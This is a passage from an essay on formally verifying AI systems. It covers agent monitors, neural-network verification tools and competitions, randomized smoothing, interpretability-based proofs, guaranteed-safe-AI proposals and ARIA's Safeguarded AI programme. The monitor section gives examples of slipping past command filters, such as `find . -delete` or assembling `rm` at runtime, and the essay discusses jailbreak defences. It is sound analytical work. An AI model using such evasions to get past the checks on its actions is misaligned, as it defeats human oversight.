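Suppose a car is travelling at 20 metres per second towards an obstacle, and the backup controller can brake at 5 m/s². The switch checks the car every 0.1 seconds. Between checks, the learned controller could accelerate at up to 3 m/s², so the car could cover 2.0 metres and reach 20.3 m/s. Braking from that speed takes 20.3²/(2 × 5) = 41.2 metres. The switch must therefore take over if the obstacle is less than about 43.2 metres away. The proof depends on the brakes, the distance sensor and the switch, but not on the learned controller.

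A software agent could have a similar backup, such as a script that restores the last saved copy of the shop's files. But no script can recall an email or reliably get a payment back, so the monitor has to stop those actions beforehand.

### Harm that a policy doesn't describe

The same action can be harmless or harmful depending on facts the monitor doesn't have. Wang and colleagues give the example of a user who asks an agent to send $100 to Bob. Bob is the user's son, but a new colleague might also be called Bob. A rule can distinguish the two Bobs only if someone has recorded which account belongs to the son.

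Shell commands are particularly hard to check because the shell is a single tool that can do almost anything. A rule might search the agent's code for `rm`, the command that deletes files, but `find . -delete` also deletes files, and a script can assemble the string `rm` as it runs. By Rice's theorem, no checker can decide correctly for every script whether it will delete something. A policy could allow only a short list of commands, but this would make a coding agent much less useful. A monitor could also check requests when they reach the operating system. It can catch every deletion there, however the agent wrote the command, but it has less information about what the deletion is for.

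Harm can also build up over many permitted steps. If a customer-service agent may give refunds of up to 50 euros, 200 such refunds cost the shop 10,000 euros. A monitor can prevent this by keeping a running total, because it can identify the exact refund that would exceed a limit. But someone has to think of the limit, and the total has to include every agent that can give refunds. People can't foresee every dangerous combination, since even 20 kinds of action can form 8,000 sequences of three. Limits on outcomes, such as the money paid out or customer records read in a day, are more reliable than rules against particular sequences because they apply to all of them.

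## Proving properties of the neural network itself

Monitors, labels and sandboxes treat the model as a black box and limit what comes out of it. A proof about the network itself could show in advance that certain outputs never occur. The usual problem has this form:

*For every input in a region R, the network's output is in an allowed set S.*

For an image classifier, R might contain every picture that can be made from one photo of a stop sign by changing each colour value by at most 1, on the usual scale from 0 to 255. S contains the outputs in which "stop sign" gets the highest score. Researchers call this property local robustness. Testing can't establish it because R contains too many pictures. Even a picture of 32 × 32 pixels has 3,072 colour values, and if each can go up by 1, go down by 1 or stay the same, there are more than 10¹⁴⁶⁵ possible pictures.

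### A network with two neurons

A neuron adds up its inputs with certain weights and then applies a simple function to the total. The most common choice in verification research is ReLU, which leaves positive numbers unchanged and turns negative numbers into 0. Consider a network with one input x between −1 and 1 and two neurons that both compute ReLU(x). The output is their difference:

y = ReLU(x) − ReLU(x)

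The output is always 0. Suppose we want software to prove that it never exceeds 0.1.

The simplest method tracks the range of each value separately. Suppose y is the difference between two neurons that always have the same value, which lies between 0 and 1. Then y is always 0, but the method proves only that −1 ≤ y ≤ 1. This bound is too loose to be useful because the method doesn't take into account that the two neurons are always equal.

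A better method writes the bounds as expressions in x. On this range, ReLU(x) is at most (x + 1)/2 and at least x/2. The output is therefore at most (x + 1)/2 − x/2 = 1/2 and, for the same reason, at least −1/2. This halves the range but still doesn't prove the property.

The last step is to split on the sign of x. If x ≥ 0, both neurons equal x, and y = x − x = 0. If x < 0, both equal 0, and y = 0 again, so the answer is now exact. Splitting wouldn't have been enough with plain ranges, which still give −1 ≤ y ≤ 1 for x between 0 and 1.

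With n neurons there can be 2ⁿ cases. For 300 neurons that is about 2 × 10⁹⁰, so practical methods differ mainly in how they avoid checking most of the cases.

### Exact search and its limits

In *Reluplex*, Katz, Barrett and colleagues (2017) verified neural networks from ACAS Xu, a prototype collision-avoidance system for unmanned aircraft. The system's 45 networks replaced a two-gigabyte table of advice. Each network has 300 ReLU neurons. It takes five numbers, such as the distance and speed of the other aircraft, and scores five pieces of advice, from "clear of conflict" to a strong turn.

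Reluplex extends the simplex method, a standard way to find numbers that satisfy a list of linear conditions. It searches for an input that breaks the property. During the search, a neuron's output may be temporarily inconsistent with its input, and Reluplex repeatedly repairs these inconsistencies. It splits on a neuron's sign only after repairing that neuron five times. Each split narrows the possible ranges of other neurons' values, and splitting on about 10% of the neurons often settled all the others.

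Katz and colleagues proved that 42 networks never advise "clear of conflict" in certain situations where another aircraft is directly ahead. Proving another property for 41 networks took about four and a half days of computing, and their prototype, Reluplex, ran out of time on four more. They also found an input for which one network's advice contradicted the original table. Because the prototype used ordinary rounded arithmetic, they don't claim that its proofs are completely sound.

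They also proved that the general problem is NP-complete, which means that a fast method for it would give fast methods for thousands of other problems for which decades of work have found none. Their proof turns a logic puzzle into a network. Suppose a, b and c are each 0 or 1. The expression 1 − ReLU(1 − a − b − c) is 1 if at least one of them is 1, and otherwise 0, so a few neurons can compute "a or b or c". A puzzle with 50 such conditions becomes a network that adds up the 50 results. The total can reach 50 exactly when the puzzle has a solution.

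One bad input is enough to show that a network breaks its rule, and anyone can confirm this by running the network once on that input. But nobody knows a general way to write a short proof that a network obeys its rule, which limits what an overseer can check.

### Bound propagation with branching

Most current tools start by computing bounds instead of running an exact search. They pass ranges or linear expressions through the network layer by layer, which is fast but can fail to prove true properties, as it did for the two neurons. *Introduction to Neural Network Verification* (2021) says such methods can make "stupid mistakes" but work well in practice.

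When the bounds are too loose to prove the property, a branch-and-bound tool picks a neuron, splits the problem by the sign of that neuron's input, and computes new bounds for each half. It discards any half in which the property is now proved and keeps splitting the rest. It stops if it finds an input that violates the property.

The leading tool, α,β-CROWN, also searches automatically for good slopes for the lines it uses as bounds. In the small example, the lower line had a slope of 1/2. A slope of 0 or 1 would have given a different bound, y ≤ 1. The tool builds the effects of earlier splits into its bounds and runs the computation on graphics processors.

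Ladner, Kaulen and colleagues (2026), in *The 7th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2026)*, compared 13 such tools. α,β-CROWN solved 3,164 of the 3,373 problems in the main track, or 94%, by proving 1,982 properties and finding counterexamples to 1,182. It solved all 186 ACAS Xu problems with less than two minutes allowed for each. Results for some of the other networks were:

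| Networks | Parameters | Problems | Solved by α,β-CROWN |
|---|---|---|---|
| Sentence classifiers | 4,000 | 1,080 | 100% |
| ACAS Xu | 13,000 | 186 | 100% |
| Small vision transformers | 68,000–76,000 | 200 | 61.5% |
| Image classifiers for 100 classes | 2.5–3.8 million | 200 | 80% |
| VGG16, a large image classifier | 138 million | 18 | 100% |

The largest language models have around a trillion parameters (weights), about 7,000 times as many as VGG16, but size is only part of the difficulty. Some of the VGG16 problems change a single pixel, which leaves most of the network's behaviour fixed. The vision transformers are tiny, yet much harder to verify. Transformers, the design behind language models, multiply computed values by each other and apply functions that are harder to bound than ReLU. To make verification feasible at all, their developers gave these two transformers only two or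 three layers and replaced a standard component with a simpler one. They also removed the easiest problems, so the solved rate would be higher on a random selection.

Another tool, ACT, reported proofs for all 200 transformer problems, but this result deserves caution because the organisers penalised ACT for ten incorrect results elsewhere, and the transformer set contains almost no false properties that could expose a faulty verifier. Eight of the 13 tools had at least one incorrect result in the main track, including α,β-CROWN, which had one. Ladner and colleagues hope eventually to require a checkable proof with every positive answer, so that users could trust a small checker instead of the whole tool, as they do with Lean.

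Engineers can make a network easier to verify by training it for verification, but this lowers its accuracy. One classifier in the competition was trained to resist changes of up to 2 steps in each colour value. It classified 83.5% of test pictures correctly, and α,β-CROWN proved it both correct and robust on 66.0%. For a version trained to resist changes of up to 8 steps, the figures were 57.2% and 35.5%.

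### Randomized smoothing

Randomized smoothing gives a weaker guarantee but requires much less computation. Jeremy Cohen, Elan Rosenfeld and Zico Kolter proved the standard version in 2019. Software makes many copies of the input, adds random noise to each from a bell curve with standard deviation σ, runs the network on each noisy copy, and returns the most common answer.

Suppose the leading answer has a probability of at least p₁ on a noisy copy, and every other answer has a probability of at most p₂. The leading answer then stays the same for every change to the input smaller than

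R = (σ/2) × (Φ⁻¹(p₁) − Φ⁻¹(p₂)).

Here the size of a change is the square root of the sum of the squared changes to each value, and Φ⁻¹(p) is the number that a standard normal variable falls below with probability p.

The formula works because moving the input a short distance d moves the cloud of noisy copies by d, so the old and new clouds mostly overlap. Even in the worst case, where the network's wrong answers lie exactly where the new cloud is denser, the leading answer keeps a probability of at least Φ(Φ⁻¹(p₁) − d/σ). If p₂ = 1 − p₁, this stays above one half as long as d is less than R = σ × Φ⁻¹(p₁).

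Suppose colour values run from 0 to 1, σ is 0.5, and the network answers "stop sign" for all 1,000 noisy copies of a photo. We can then be 99.9% confident that p₁ is at least 0.993, because 0.993¹⁰⁰⁰ is about 0.001. This gives R ≈ 1.23. If a photo has 150,528 colour values and an attacker changes them all equally, the guarantee covers less than one step out of 255 in each. With 100,000 copies and the same unanimous answer, R rises only to about 1.9.

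The method scales well because it uses only the network's outputs. It takes 1,000 runs, whatever the network's design. But the guarantee has a small chance of being wrong because it depends on a random sample. It also applies only to the majority vote, not to a single run. Adding more noise widens the protected region but makes the pictures harder to classify.

Text creates a further problem because we can add a little noise to a colour value but not to the word "refund". *Provable Defense Framework for LLM Jailbreaks via Noise-Augumented Alignment* (2026) notes that the standard noise is therefore poorly defined for language models, so a guarantee for text needs a different mathematical basis.

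SmoothLLM defends against jailbreaks, which are prompts designed to get past a model's safety training. It randomly changes characters in copies of the prompt and combines the model's responses. Its original guarantee assumes that an attack always fails once at least k characters have changed. According to *Towards Realistic Guarantees* (2025), this rarely holds in practice. In its tests, attack success rates fell gradually as more characters changed instead of dropping to zero. The paper therefore derives a guarantee from the measured rates for two types of attack. This guarantee is more realistic, but success rates for a new type of attack might fall differently.

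### Proofs that use an explanation of the network

The methods so far use little knowledge of what a network has learned. Gross, Agrawal and colleagues (2024), in *Compact Proofs of Model Performance via Mechanistic Interpretability*, tested whether such knowledge makes proofs shorter. Mechanistic interpretability means working out from a network's weights what algorithm it uses.

Researchers trained 151 small transformers to find the largest of four whole numbers between 0 and 63. Each model has a single layer. Its attention mechanism, which sets how much each input number counts, gives a number about 3.4 times as much weight as a number that is smaller by one. The model then copies the number with the most weight, which is usually the largest.

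The aim was to prove a lower bound on accuracy over all 64⁴ (about 16.8 million) inputs. Running the model on every input gives the exact accuracy, but this was feasible only for inputs of up to four numbers.

A shorter proof uses the model's structure. For the input 5, 9, 60, 12, the proof considers simpler inputs that have the same largest and last numbers but at most one other value, such as 5, 5, 60, 12 and 9, 9, 60, 12. Gross and colleagues proved that if the model answers 60 for all such inputs, it must also answer 60 for the original. The proof therefore needs to check only combinations of three numbers. Even shorter proofs use more of the explanation, for example that attention depends almost entirely on a number's size.

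| Proof | Arithmetic operations | Accuracy proved (average) | Unexplained dimensions |
|---|---|---|---|
| Run every input | 2⁴⁷ | 99.9% | 2³⁰ |
| Combinations of three numbers | 2²⁵ | 95.3% | 2¹⁴ |
| Combinations of two numbers | 2²¹ | 70.2% | 2¹³ |

The last column estimates how many numbers are still needed to describe the model's behaviour, given the explanation. Shorter proofs leave less unexplained but prove less. Understanding the model better can partly make up for this. The 70.2% in the last row relies on knowing which parts of the model barely vary. Without that knowledge, a proof with about the same amount of arithmetic establishes only 34.9%.

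The bounds weaken because the explanation is never quite complete. After Gross and colleagues described the main pattern in each weight matrix, small irregular errors remained. In the real model these errors mostly cancel, but without an account of why they cancel, a proof has to use the worst case. For example, 100 errors of size 1 with random signs typically add up to about 10, but a bound that covers every combination of signs must allow for 100. When the researchers simplified several matrices separately, the worst-case error became orders of magnitude larger than the actual error, and the proof established nothing useful. They suspect that there is often no short explanation for why such errors cancel.

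*Evaluating Explanations* (2025) describes the method as a program that takes the network's weights and an explanation and returns a guaranteed bound. If the explanation is wrong, the bound is weaker but still holds, so the explanation doesn't have to be trusted. An AI system could therefore propose explanations, just as Claude proposes proofs to Rocq.

### From toy tasks towards language models

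*Modular addition without black-boxes* (2024) extends the approach to harder networks, which add numbers as on a clock face, so that 9 + 5 gives 2. Earlier work had described one layer of some of these networks by running through every possible input, which becomes infeasible as the range of numbers grows. The newer paper explains that layer as a way of approximating an integral.

*Interactions Between Crosscoder Features* (2026) tackles the need to write a new proof by hand for every model and task. It uses a crosscoder, a second network trained to describe the first one's internal values, across many layers, as combinations of a limited set of features. The paper shows how to turn such a description into a proof. Errors again build up. If a layer can multiply incoming errors by at most K, then

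error after the layer ≤ K × error before it + the layer's own error.

If K = 2 and each layer adds an error of 0.01, the bound after ten layers is about 10. In experiments on a 33-million-parameter model that writes children's stories, the method gave useful bounds for one type of layer on its own but none for the whole model.

The same paper trains crosscoders to avoid overlaps between features, which cause part of the error. With this training, keeping only the strongest feature at each neuron preserved about 60% of a layer's performance, compared with 10% for an ordinary crosscoder. The resulting descriptions should be easier to use in proofs, though the model itself stays the same.

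Another option is to change the model. *Towards Verifiable Transformers* (2026) took a model the size of GPT-2, a language model from 2019, and replaced one mechanism for handling quotation marks with a small program. It then proved that the modified model behaves as specified on a fixed list of 1,280 prompts, even if certain internal values change slightly. The paper states that this doesn't verify the original GPT-2.

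*Certified Mechanistic Interpretability* (2026) examines whether a finding about one input also holds for a region of inputs around it. Its results suggest that the shape of the region matters a great deal. In BERT-tiny, a very small language model, a region built from five paraphrases of a sentence could distinguish between two parts of the attention mechanism, while one that allowed equal changes in every direction was too crude to do so.

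None of this comes close to a proof about everything a language model might write. With a vocabulary of 100,000 tokens, there are 10⁵⁰⁰⁰ possible prompts of 1,000 tokens, and an agent's context can be much longer.

### Could AI write the proofs?

The October study of open-source libraries showed that AI systems have already removed one limit, the shortage of people to do the work. In VNN-COMP, Vibecheck, a verifier that two researchers made in two months, mostly with Claude Opus 4.8, took second place. It solved 3,108 problems in the main track, 56 fewer than α,β-CROWN, and had no incorrect results. AI could also search for explanations of networks far faster than people can.

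But a better prover can't find a short proof if none exists. If a network's errors cancel for no describable reason, a proof has to track them through the weights, and the work grows with the network's size. The NP-completeness result also applies to every prover, human or artificial. However, it concerns the hardest networks, and trained ones may be easier to verify.

AI may therefore help more by redesigning networks so that short proofs exist. The image classifiers and the GPT-2-sized model show that this is possible on a small scale, but it is unknown how much ability a large language model would lose in the process. Gross and colleagues suggest an alternative, replacing worst-case proofs with arguments about what typically happens. These arguments could be much shorter, but they would not rule out failures on atypical inputs, which are the ones an attacker looks for.

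### Properties without a formula

A property must be stated formally before it can be proved. Gross and colleagues say their method covers any aspect of performance "for which we have a formal specification". "The answer is the largest of the four numbers" is easy to write as a formula, but "the answer is honest" is hard because honesty depends on what the model represents as true, and nobody can yet define that in terms of its weights. Harmlessness is also hard to specify because it depends on facts outside the text. For example, the same paragraph about drug doses can help a nurse and endanger someone else.

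Researchers sometimes use a substitute that does have a formula. The sentence classifiers in VNN-COMP are meant to recognise, for example, when a user asks whether they are talking to a machine. A language model first turns each sentence into a list of 30 numbers. The property is that the classifier gives the right answer at every point in a box around a sentence and its reworded versions. α,β-CROWN settled all 1,080 of these problems, and 662 of the properties were false. But a box can contain points that match no real sentence, so a counterexample may be harmless. The classifier may also fail on a real sentence despite a proof, because the box can leave out a rewording that nobody thought of.

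Another substitute is to use a second network to judge the first. One set of problems in the competition concerns a network that draws a car at a requested distance. The formula can't express how far away the car looks, so it requires another network's estimate to be close to the requested distance. If that estimate is wrong, the proof still holds, but the picture shows the car at the wrong distance. A proof that a language model's answers satisfy an AI judge of honesty would have the same weakness, and the judge would be a large network with its own blind spots.

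Writing the formula can be difficult even for aircraft. One property Katz and colleagues tested was that "clear of conflict" should never be the worst-rated advice when the other aircraft is distant and much slower. Reluplex found violations in 35 networks. This behaviour later turned out to be acceptable, because the networks are designed with a bias towards repeating their previous advice. The engineers could resolve this because they knew what the system was for and the property was simple. AI-written proofs wouldn't have helped them, because the proof technology had correctly found violations of a faulty requirement.

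Some properties of the shop's agent can be written as a formula, such as "never request a transfer to an account that isn't on the list." In principle, someone could try to prove that the agent obeys this rule for every possible bug report, but a monitor outside the model can already enforce it for any model, with almost no overhead. A monitor can usually enforce any rule about outputs that is clear enough to prove.

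Proofs about the network are more valuable when refusing an action isn't safe, or when the property compares several inputs. For example, an aircraft in danger needs good advice, so rejecting bad advice isn't enough, although a shield can sometimes help. Robustness compares the answers to similar inputs, so a monitor can't check it, just as it can't check noninterference. Small networks with numerical inputs, like those in ACAS Xu, are therefore the best candidates for this kind of proof.

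The physicist Max Tegmark argues in the talk *Provably Safe AI* that people should stop assuming they will deploy more powerful networks directly. A network can instead produce an ordinary program, which people can verify and run without the network. The shop's refund function is such a program, but no one knows how to write one that reads a customer's complaint as well as the agent does.

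## Proposals to guarantee the safety of whole AI systems

A proof about a neural network covers only its outputs. Proving that those outputs won't cause harm also requires a mathematical description of how they affect the world. For a medical pump, this includes what the drug does in the patient's body. *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI* (Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues, 2024) proposes such proofs for AI systems in general.

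They think testing alone is too weak for dangerous systems. ChatGPT went through months of evaluation, but users got past its safeguards within a day of its release. They also point out that about a quarter of the bridges built in the 1870s collapsed within the decade, before better theory reduced the failure rate to less than 0.4% per decade.

### World model, specification and verifier

One of the proposal's three parts is a world model, which takes a state of the world and an action and returns the probabilities of what happens next. Where nobody knows the probabilities, it can return a set of possibilities instead. For example, nobody can predict when another driver will brake, so the model can allow any braking that driver's car is capable of, and the safety proof then has to cover every case.

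The safety specification gives a score between 0 and 1, written ψ(π, m), to each combination of a policy π and a world model m. The policy is the rule by which the AI system picks its actions, and it can be a neural network that nobody understands. The score could be the probability that no patient gets an overdose within a year. The verifier calculates a range for this score and gives evidence that others can check. The system passes if the whole range is acceptable, such as 0.9999 to 1.

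Dalrymple and colleagues rank the ways to build each part by how much safety they would provide. These are some of the levels:

| Part | Weak | Intermediate | Strongest |
|---|---|---|---|
| World model (0–5) | a trained simulator that nobody can inspect (1) | causal models that experts have fully audited (3) | no model, because the specification holds in every possible world (5) |
| Specification (0–7) | plain language that a black-box AI interprets (2) | hand-written rules for a few limited properties (3) | everything people might want, in every context (7) |
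| Verifier (0–10) | improvised tests (1) | sampling that would cover every input if it ran forever (6) | a proof or sound bound that people can read and check (10) |

They require a verifier at level 8 or above for strong guarantees. A level 8 verifier can stop after a finite time and quantify how much it has left uncovered. A level 9 verifier gives an upper limit on the probability of failure, and that limit is certain to be correct if the world model is correct.

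One way to reach level 9 is to give every state a danger score of zero or more. The score must be at least 1 in every unsafe state, and on average it must never rise from one step to the next. If it starts at 0.001, the chance of reaching an unsafe state is at most 0.001, because a higher chance would push the average above 0.001. Finding a suitable score is hard, but a neural network can learn one, and a separate program can then check both conditions. Ammann calls this a neural certificate in *Safeguarded AI* (2026). The check has to cover every state, so it is difficult for large networks for the same reasons as other network proofs.

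### Is proof the only path?

In *Provably safe systems*, Tegmark and Omohundro (2023) argue that proof is the only way to control artificial general intelligence (AGI), meaning AI that can do most things people can do.

They want to extend proof-carrying code from single programs to the world's infrastructure. AI chips would run only programs that come with a proof that they obey agreed rules. DNA synthesizers would make only DNA that comes with a proof of safety, and drones wouldn't take off without such a proof. Most of the programs would be ordinary code instead of neural networks, an idea that Tegmark also defends in the talk *Provably Safe AI*. There he describes a small demonstration in which software extracted a Python program from a network that had learned to add numbers, and researchers proved the program correct in Dafny.

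Tegmark and Omohundro's argument that provably safe systems are the only path to controllable AGI relies on Gödel's completeness theorem, which says that any statement true in every model of a set of axioms has a proof from those axioms. They conclude that if a safety property has no proof, there must be a way to violate it, which a powerful AI may well find.

This doesn't follow for real systems. The theorem guarantees a violation in some mathematical model of the axioms, but that model may not match the real world. A system can be safe because of a fact the axioms omit. A proof can also exist but be too long for anyone to find.

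Dalrymple and colleagues, who include Tegmark and Omohundro, accept a limit on the probability of harm instead of requiring proof that harm is impossible. They also allow the AI system to remain a black box, and they recommend using their approach alongside testing and other methods.

### A worked example: a painkiller pump

Suppose a hospital pump gives a painkiller once an hour, and a neural network chooses each dose from the patient's heart rate and reported pain. A guarantee could have these parts:

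- **World model:** each hour, the body removes a fraction k of the drug, where k is between 0.1 and 0.3. A dose then raises the concentration by u milligrams per litre, so the new concentration is (1 − k) × the old one + u.
- **Specification:** the concentration never exceeds 10 mg/l.
- **Verifier:** a proof about the network together with a small program that limits u to 1, whatever the network requests.

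The proof uses the invariant that the concentration is at most 10. The concentration starts at 0, and if it is at most 10 before a dose, it is at most 0.9 × 10 + 1 = 10 afterwards. It therefore stays within the limit after any number of doses.

The proof depends most on the assumption that k is at least 0.1. For a patient whose kidneys are failing and whose k is only 0.05, the proof would still be mathematically valid but wouldn't apply. Doses of 1 mg/l would take that patient's concentration past 10 at the 14th dose and eventually close to 20.

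The hospital could make the model more conservative by allowing k to be as low as 0.05 and limiting each dose to 0.5. But in a patient whose body removes 30% of the drug every hour, the concentration could then reach only about 1.7 instead of 3.3, which might be too low to relieve pain.

It could also check the model while the pump is running. Dalrymple and colleagues suggest monitoring for signs that the world model is wrong and switching to a backup if any appear. After eight doses of 1 mg/l, the model predicts a concentration of at most 5.7 mg/l. The patient with failing kidneys would have reached 6.7 mg/l, so a blood test would reveal the problem while the concentration was still safe. The pump could then stop and alert a nurse.

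### Can people model the world accurately enough?

In *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety*, Dickson (2024) doubts that anyone will soon obtain strong guarantees against the most serious AI threats. He gives the example of the Perseverance rover, which landed on Mars in 2021. Engineers used a verification tool to show that bugs in the lander's software wouldn't make it fail. But according to one analysis, software accounts for only about 20% of the risk in Mars missions, so the tool couldn't help with the rest.

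Living things are harder to model than spacecraft. In 2022, a leading simulation covered 20 minutes in the life of one unusually simple cell. A human body has about 36 trillion cells. Even a perfect model would need data about the initial state of the system it simulates. Google researchers spent years mapping a millionth of a human brain, and the data took up 1.4 petabytes.

In the discussion of *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety*, Omohundro replies that physicists already know all the laws that matter in everyday life, and that engineers can design systems to be easy to verify. Another participant answers that these laws don't provide usable models of large objects. For example, nobody could work out from quantum field theory alone how water freezes under pressure. Dalrymple and colleagues acknowledge the related problem that even someone with a perfect knowledge of physics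 couldn't tell whether a molecule is toxic without facts about human cells.

*On Controllability of AI* (2020) quotes the AI researcher Ben Goertzel's worry that a future revision of physics could make a safety proof irrelevant. This risk seems smaller than that of a wrong assumption about the system's surroundings, because any new theory would have to agree with the many experiments that support the current ones. The pump's guarantee, for example, is far more likely to fail because a patient's kidneys don't work as the proof assumes.

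A narrower safety guarantee can avoid the modelling problem. A reader of Dickson's essay correctly objects that one could prove, without simulating a human body, that a DNA synthesizer will refuse to make certain known pathogens. However, the synthesizer could still make a new pathogen. Dalrymple and colleagues also propose an AI system that would limit the risk from any given sequence, and Dickson's objection applies fully to that proposal.

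A guarantee can also account for uncertainty about the model. Dalrymple and colleagues point out that if the model has a probability of at most ε of being wrong at each step, and the verifier proves a system safe for n steps, the real system is safe with a probability of at least (1 − ε)ⁿ. With one-hour steps and an ε of 0.0001, this lower bound is 99.3% for three days but 42% for a year. Approving a system for a short period and then checking it again is therefore much easier to justify than approving it for a long one.

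But ε is an estimate that the verifier can't prove. An estimate based on past experience may also be too low, because an AI system that searches a model for the best plan tends to find places where the model is too optimistic. Dickson says that engineers' figures for bridges are also estimates, not guarantees. He is wrong to suggest that his opponents generally expect a failure rate of zero, since Dalrymple and colleagues explicitly allow probabilities. But a probability that depends on an estimated ε is weaker than the word "guaranteed" implies.

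Dalrymple and colleagues also argue that if an AI system can reliably carry out complicated, dangerous plans, then it must be possible to model the world accurately. But a planner needs to find only one plan that works, while a safety guarantee has to cover every way things could go wrong. The planner's knowledge may also be stored in a network that nobody can interpret.

AI could help build the models, but Dickson thinks major help with modelling will come only with superintelligence, which would be too late. He does expect AI to help with proofs, and the October study of open-source libraries supports this. The evidence on modelling is less encouraging, because AI-written models of existing software often fail to match the real system, and software is much easier to describe than a human body.

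### Can people define harm?

Dalrymple and colleagues offer a starting point for defining harm. Each outcome has a value between 0 and 1, and a default value represents what people would normally expect. An action causes harm if it leads to an outcome below the default and some other action would have led to a better one.

Suppose comfort has a value of 1, pain 0.4 and an overdose 0. If the pump withholds a dose that would have relieved the patient's pain, it does harm if the default is 0.5 but not if the default is 0.3. People who disagree about whether withholding a painkiller is harmful will also disagree about the default.

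Harm to distant systems is even harder to specify. In the discussion of Dickson's essay, one participant imagines trying to prove that a program will never trigger a bug in a database server somewhere on the internet. Each message the program sends might look harmless, and the person writing the specification doesn't know the bug exists. Dickson raises a similar problem with misinformation, since a genuine photo can mislead people when someone shows it out of context.

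One approach is to specify safety for the whole system rather than for each part. Seshia, Sadigh and Sastry recommend this in *Toward Verified Artificial Intelligence* (2022), a research agenda with 15 principles that Dalrymple and colleagues summarise. Nobody can write a formula for what a pedestrian looks like, but "the car doesn't hit anything" is much easier to formalise. Engineers might prove that a car never hits anything as long as its vision network reports every obstacle within 50 metres. They could then test the network for the errors that matter most, which are missed obstacles within that range.

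Another approach is to use a rule that is stricter than necessary, like the pump's limit of 10 mg/l. AI systems could also suggest rules and find cases where two of them give different results, so that people can choose between them. These methods work best when the job is narrow. A general assistant gives advice on almost anything, and no one has a short list of limits that would make all its advice safe.

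### Is the proved system the one in use?

A buyer might receive a DNA synthesizer and a valid proof that it can't make certain pathogens. Dickson asks how the buyer can know that the proof describes this particular machine, since it might have a manufacturing defect or a hidden back door. The problem is worse for a chatbot on the internet, because the user can't inspect the computer it runs on. He concludes that such proofs would require intensive, continuous physical inspections.

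Tegmark and Omohundro want hardware that detects tampering and then erases its cryptographic keys, so it can no longer authorise anything. This would make an approved machine harder to alter, though the buyer would still have to trust the factory. Ammann lists the problem among the programme's open challenges and suggests drawing on research into supply-chain security and confidential computing (hardware that protects data and code while they are in use). The problem is easier for software alone, because a trusted device can check that it is about to run exactly the bytes the proof covers.

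### What about general-purpose AI?

The talk *Formal Verification is Overrated* supports using AI to write verified software, but argues that this can't replace work on the safety of AI itself. A company that used only verified programs would be at a disadvantage to rivals that used general-purpose AI.

Tegmark and Omohundro think verified programs could compete with neural networks. They argue that neural networks are powerful because they are good at learning, and that once a network has found a good algorithm, ordinary code can run it just as efficiently. But holding a conversation is much more complex than adding numbers, and nobody has turned a large language model into ordinary code that people can verify.

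Dalrymple and colleagues avoid this problem by keeping the general model and checking what it proposes. For example, the model could design a new schedule for a power grid, and a verifier would reject any schedule that might overload a line. This works where people have a world model and a specification. They have neither for a request such as "help me with this difficult letter", so the system must refuse or answer without a guarantee.

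### The Safeguarded AI programme

The UK's Advanced Research and Invention Agency (ARIA) has put £59 million into its Safeguarded AI programme, which started in mid-2024 under Dalrymple and is due to end in 2027. The original plan was to build "gatekeepers", which release an AI system's output only after verifying it against a world model and a specification. ARIA (2024) wanted to show that AI with such guarantees can bring economic benefits that ordinary AI doesn't. According to Ammann, who now directs the programme, the larger hope was to build agreement that people should deploy powerful AI only through gatekeepers.

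In November 2025, the programme cancelled its machine-learning part. Dalrymple writes in ARIA's *AI progress and a Safeguarded AI pivot* (2025) that he had expected to reject every applicant, because ordinary AI models would soon have most of the abilities the programme had planned to develop. In 2026, the programme also dropped a planned second round of physical applications. According to ARIA's *Safeguarded AI* website, rapid progress had disproved the hypothesis that developers might not make high-risk AI openly available. Ammann adds that timely international agreement on gatekeepers had become less likely.

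The table combines information from ARIA and from the University of Oxford's *Oxford researchers awarded ARIA funding to develop safety-first AI* (2025):

| Part | Plan | Position in late 2026 |
|---|---|---|
| Theory | common languages for world models, specifications and proofs | 22 projects, seven of which had closed by August |
| Machine learning | £18 million for one organisation to develop AI for gatekeepers | cancelled, with the money moved to tools |
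| Physical applications | gatekeepers for uses such as power grids and clinical trials | nine teams funded in 2025, but no second round |
| Cybersecurity | not a separate part of the original plan | eight projects with £22 million |

Much of this is still a plan. ARIA wants the theory teams to produce a single, dissertation-length definition of their languages, and Ammann still described this as a goal in May 2026. *ARIA SAGEflex* aims to make AI safe enough to coordinate many small devices on a power grid. It says the lack of safety guarantees currently prevents companies from adopting such systems. Its first objective is to develop test problems.

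A team working on pharmaceutical supply chains has made more progress. It interviewed more than 80 professionals, built mathematical models of their processes, and is now working with companies on possible products. But ARIA has not announced a working AI system with a proved limit on the harm it can do in the physical world, so the programme hasn't yet tested the most ambitious part of the proposal.

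The cybersecurity projects range from containing AI agents to protecting code on millions of Android devices. ARIA is also inviting more teams to build, in eight-week sprints, security software with machine-checked proofs. A separate team will attack each system to look for weaknesses the proofs don't cover.

### Verifying only the software

In its cybersecurity work, ARIA has moved towards a more limited version of the proposal, which verifies the software around an AI model but not the model's effects on the world. The world model then describes a processor, an operating system and what an attacker can do. The specification might be that no message from the internet can make a program leak its keys. The October study already has this form. Its world model describes a RISC-V processor and Linux, and its specification is "the program ends normally".

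Dickson's objections have much less force here. People designed the processor and can describe it far more accurately than a human body, and a leaked key is easier to define than harm. Dickson himself expects code verification to remain useful.

*From Patching Bugs to Proving Them Gone* (Ammann, 2026) describes a real demonstration of formal verification in HACMS, a programme DARPA ran from 2012 to 2017. It produced verified flight-control software, including software for a helicopter that carried people, and expert attackers couldn't break it. The proofs took a lot of human work, which AI can now reduce. Ammann cautions that each proof still depends on its specification and assumptions, and that getting these right for a real system remains hard.

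Omohundro says he too is focused on protecting infrastructure from attacks by AI. Another participant in the discussion of Dickson's essay calls this a partial solution, because an AI system with bad intentions could act outside the protected infrastructure or build its own. Omohundro agrees that hidden AI systems could be a huge problem. His long-term design requires every AI to run on proven infrastructure, and he expects the greatest risk to come before that infrastructure exists.

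Verified software could guarantee that no dose from the hospital's pump exceeds the limit and that nobody can change the limit over the network. Doctors would still have to judge from medical evidence and blood tests whether the limit is safe for a patient with failing kidneys.
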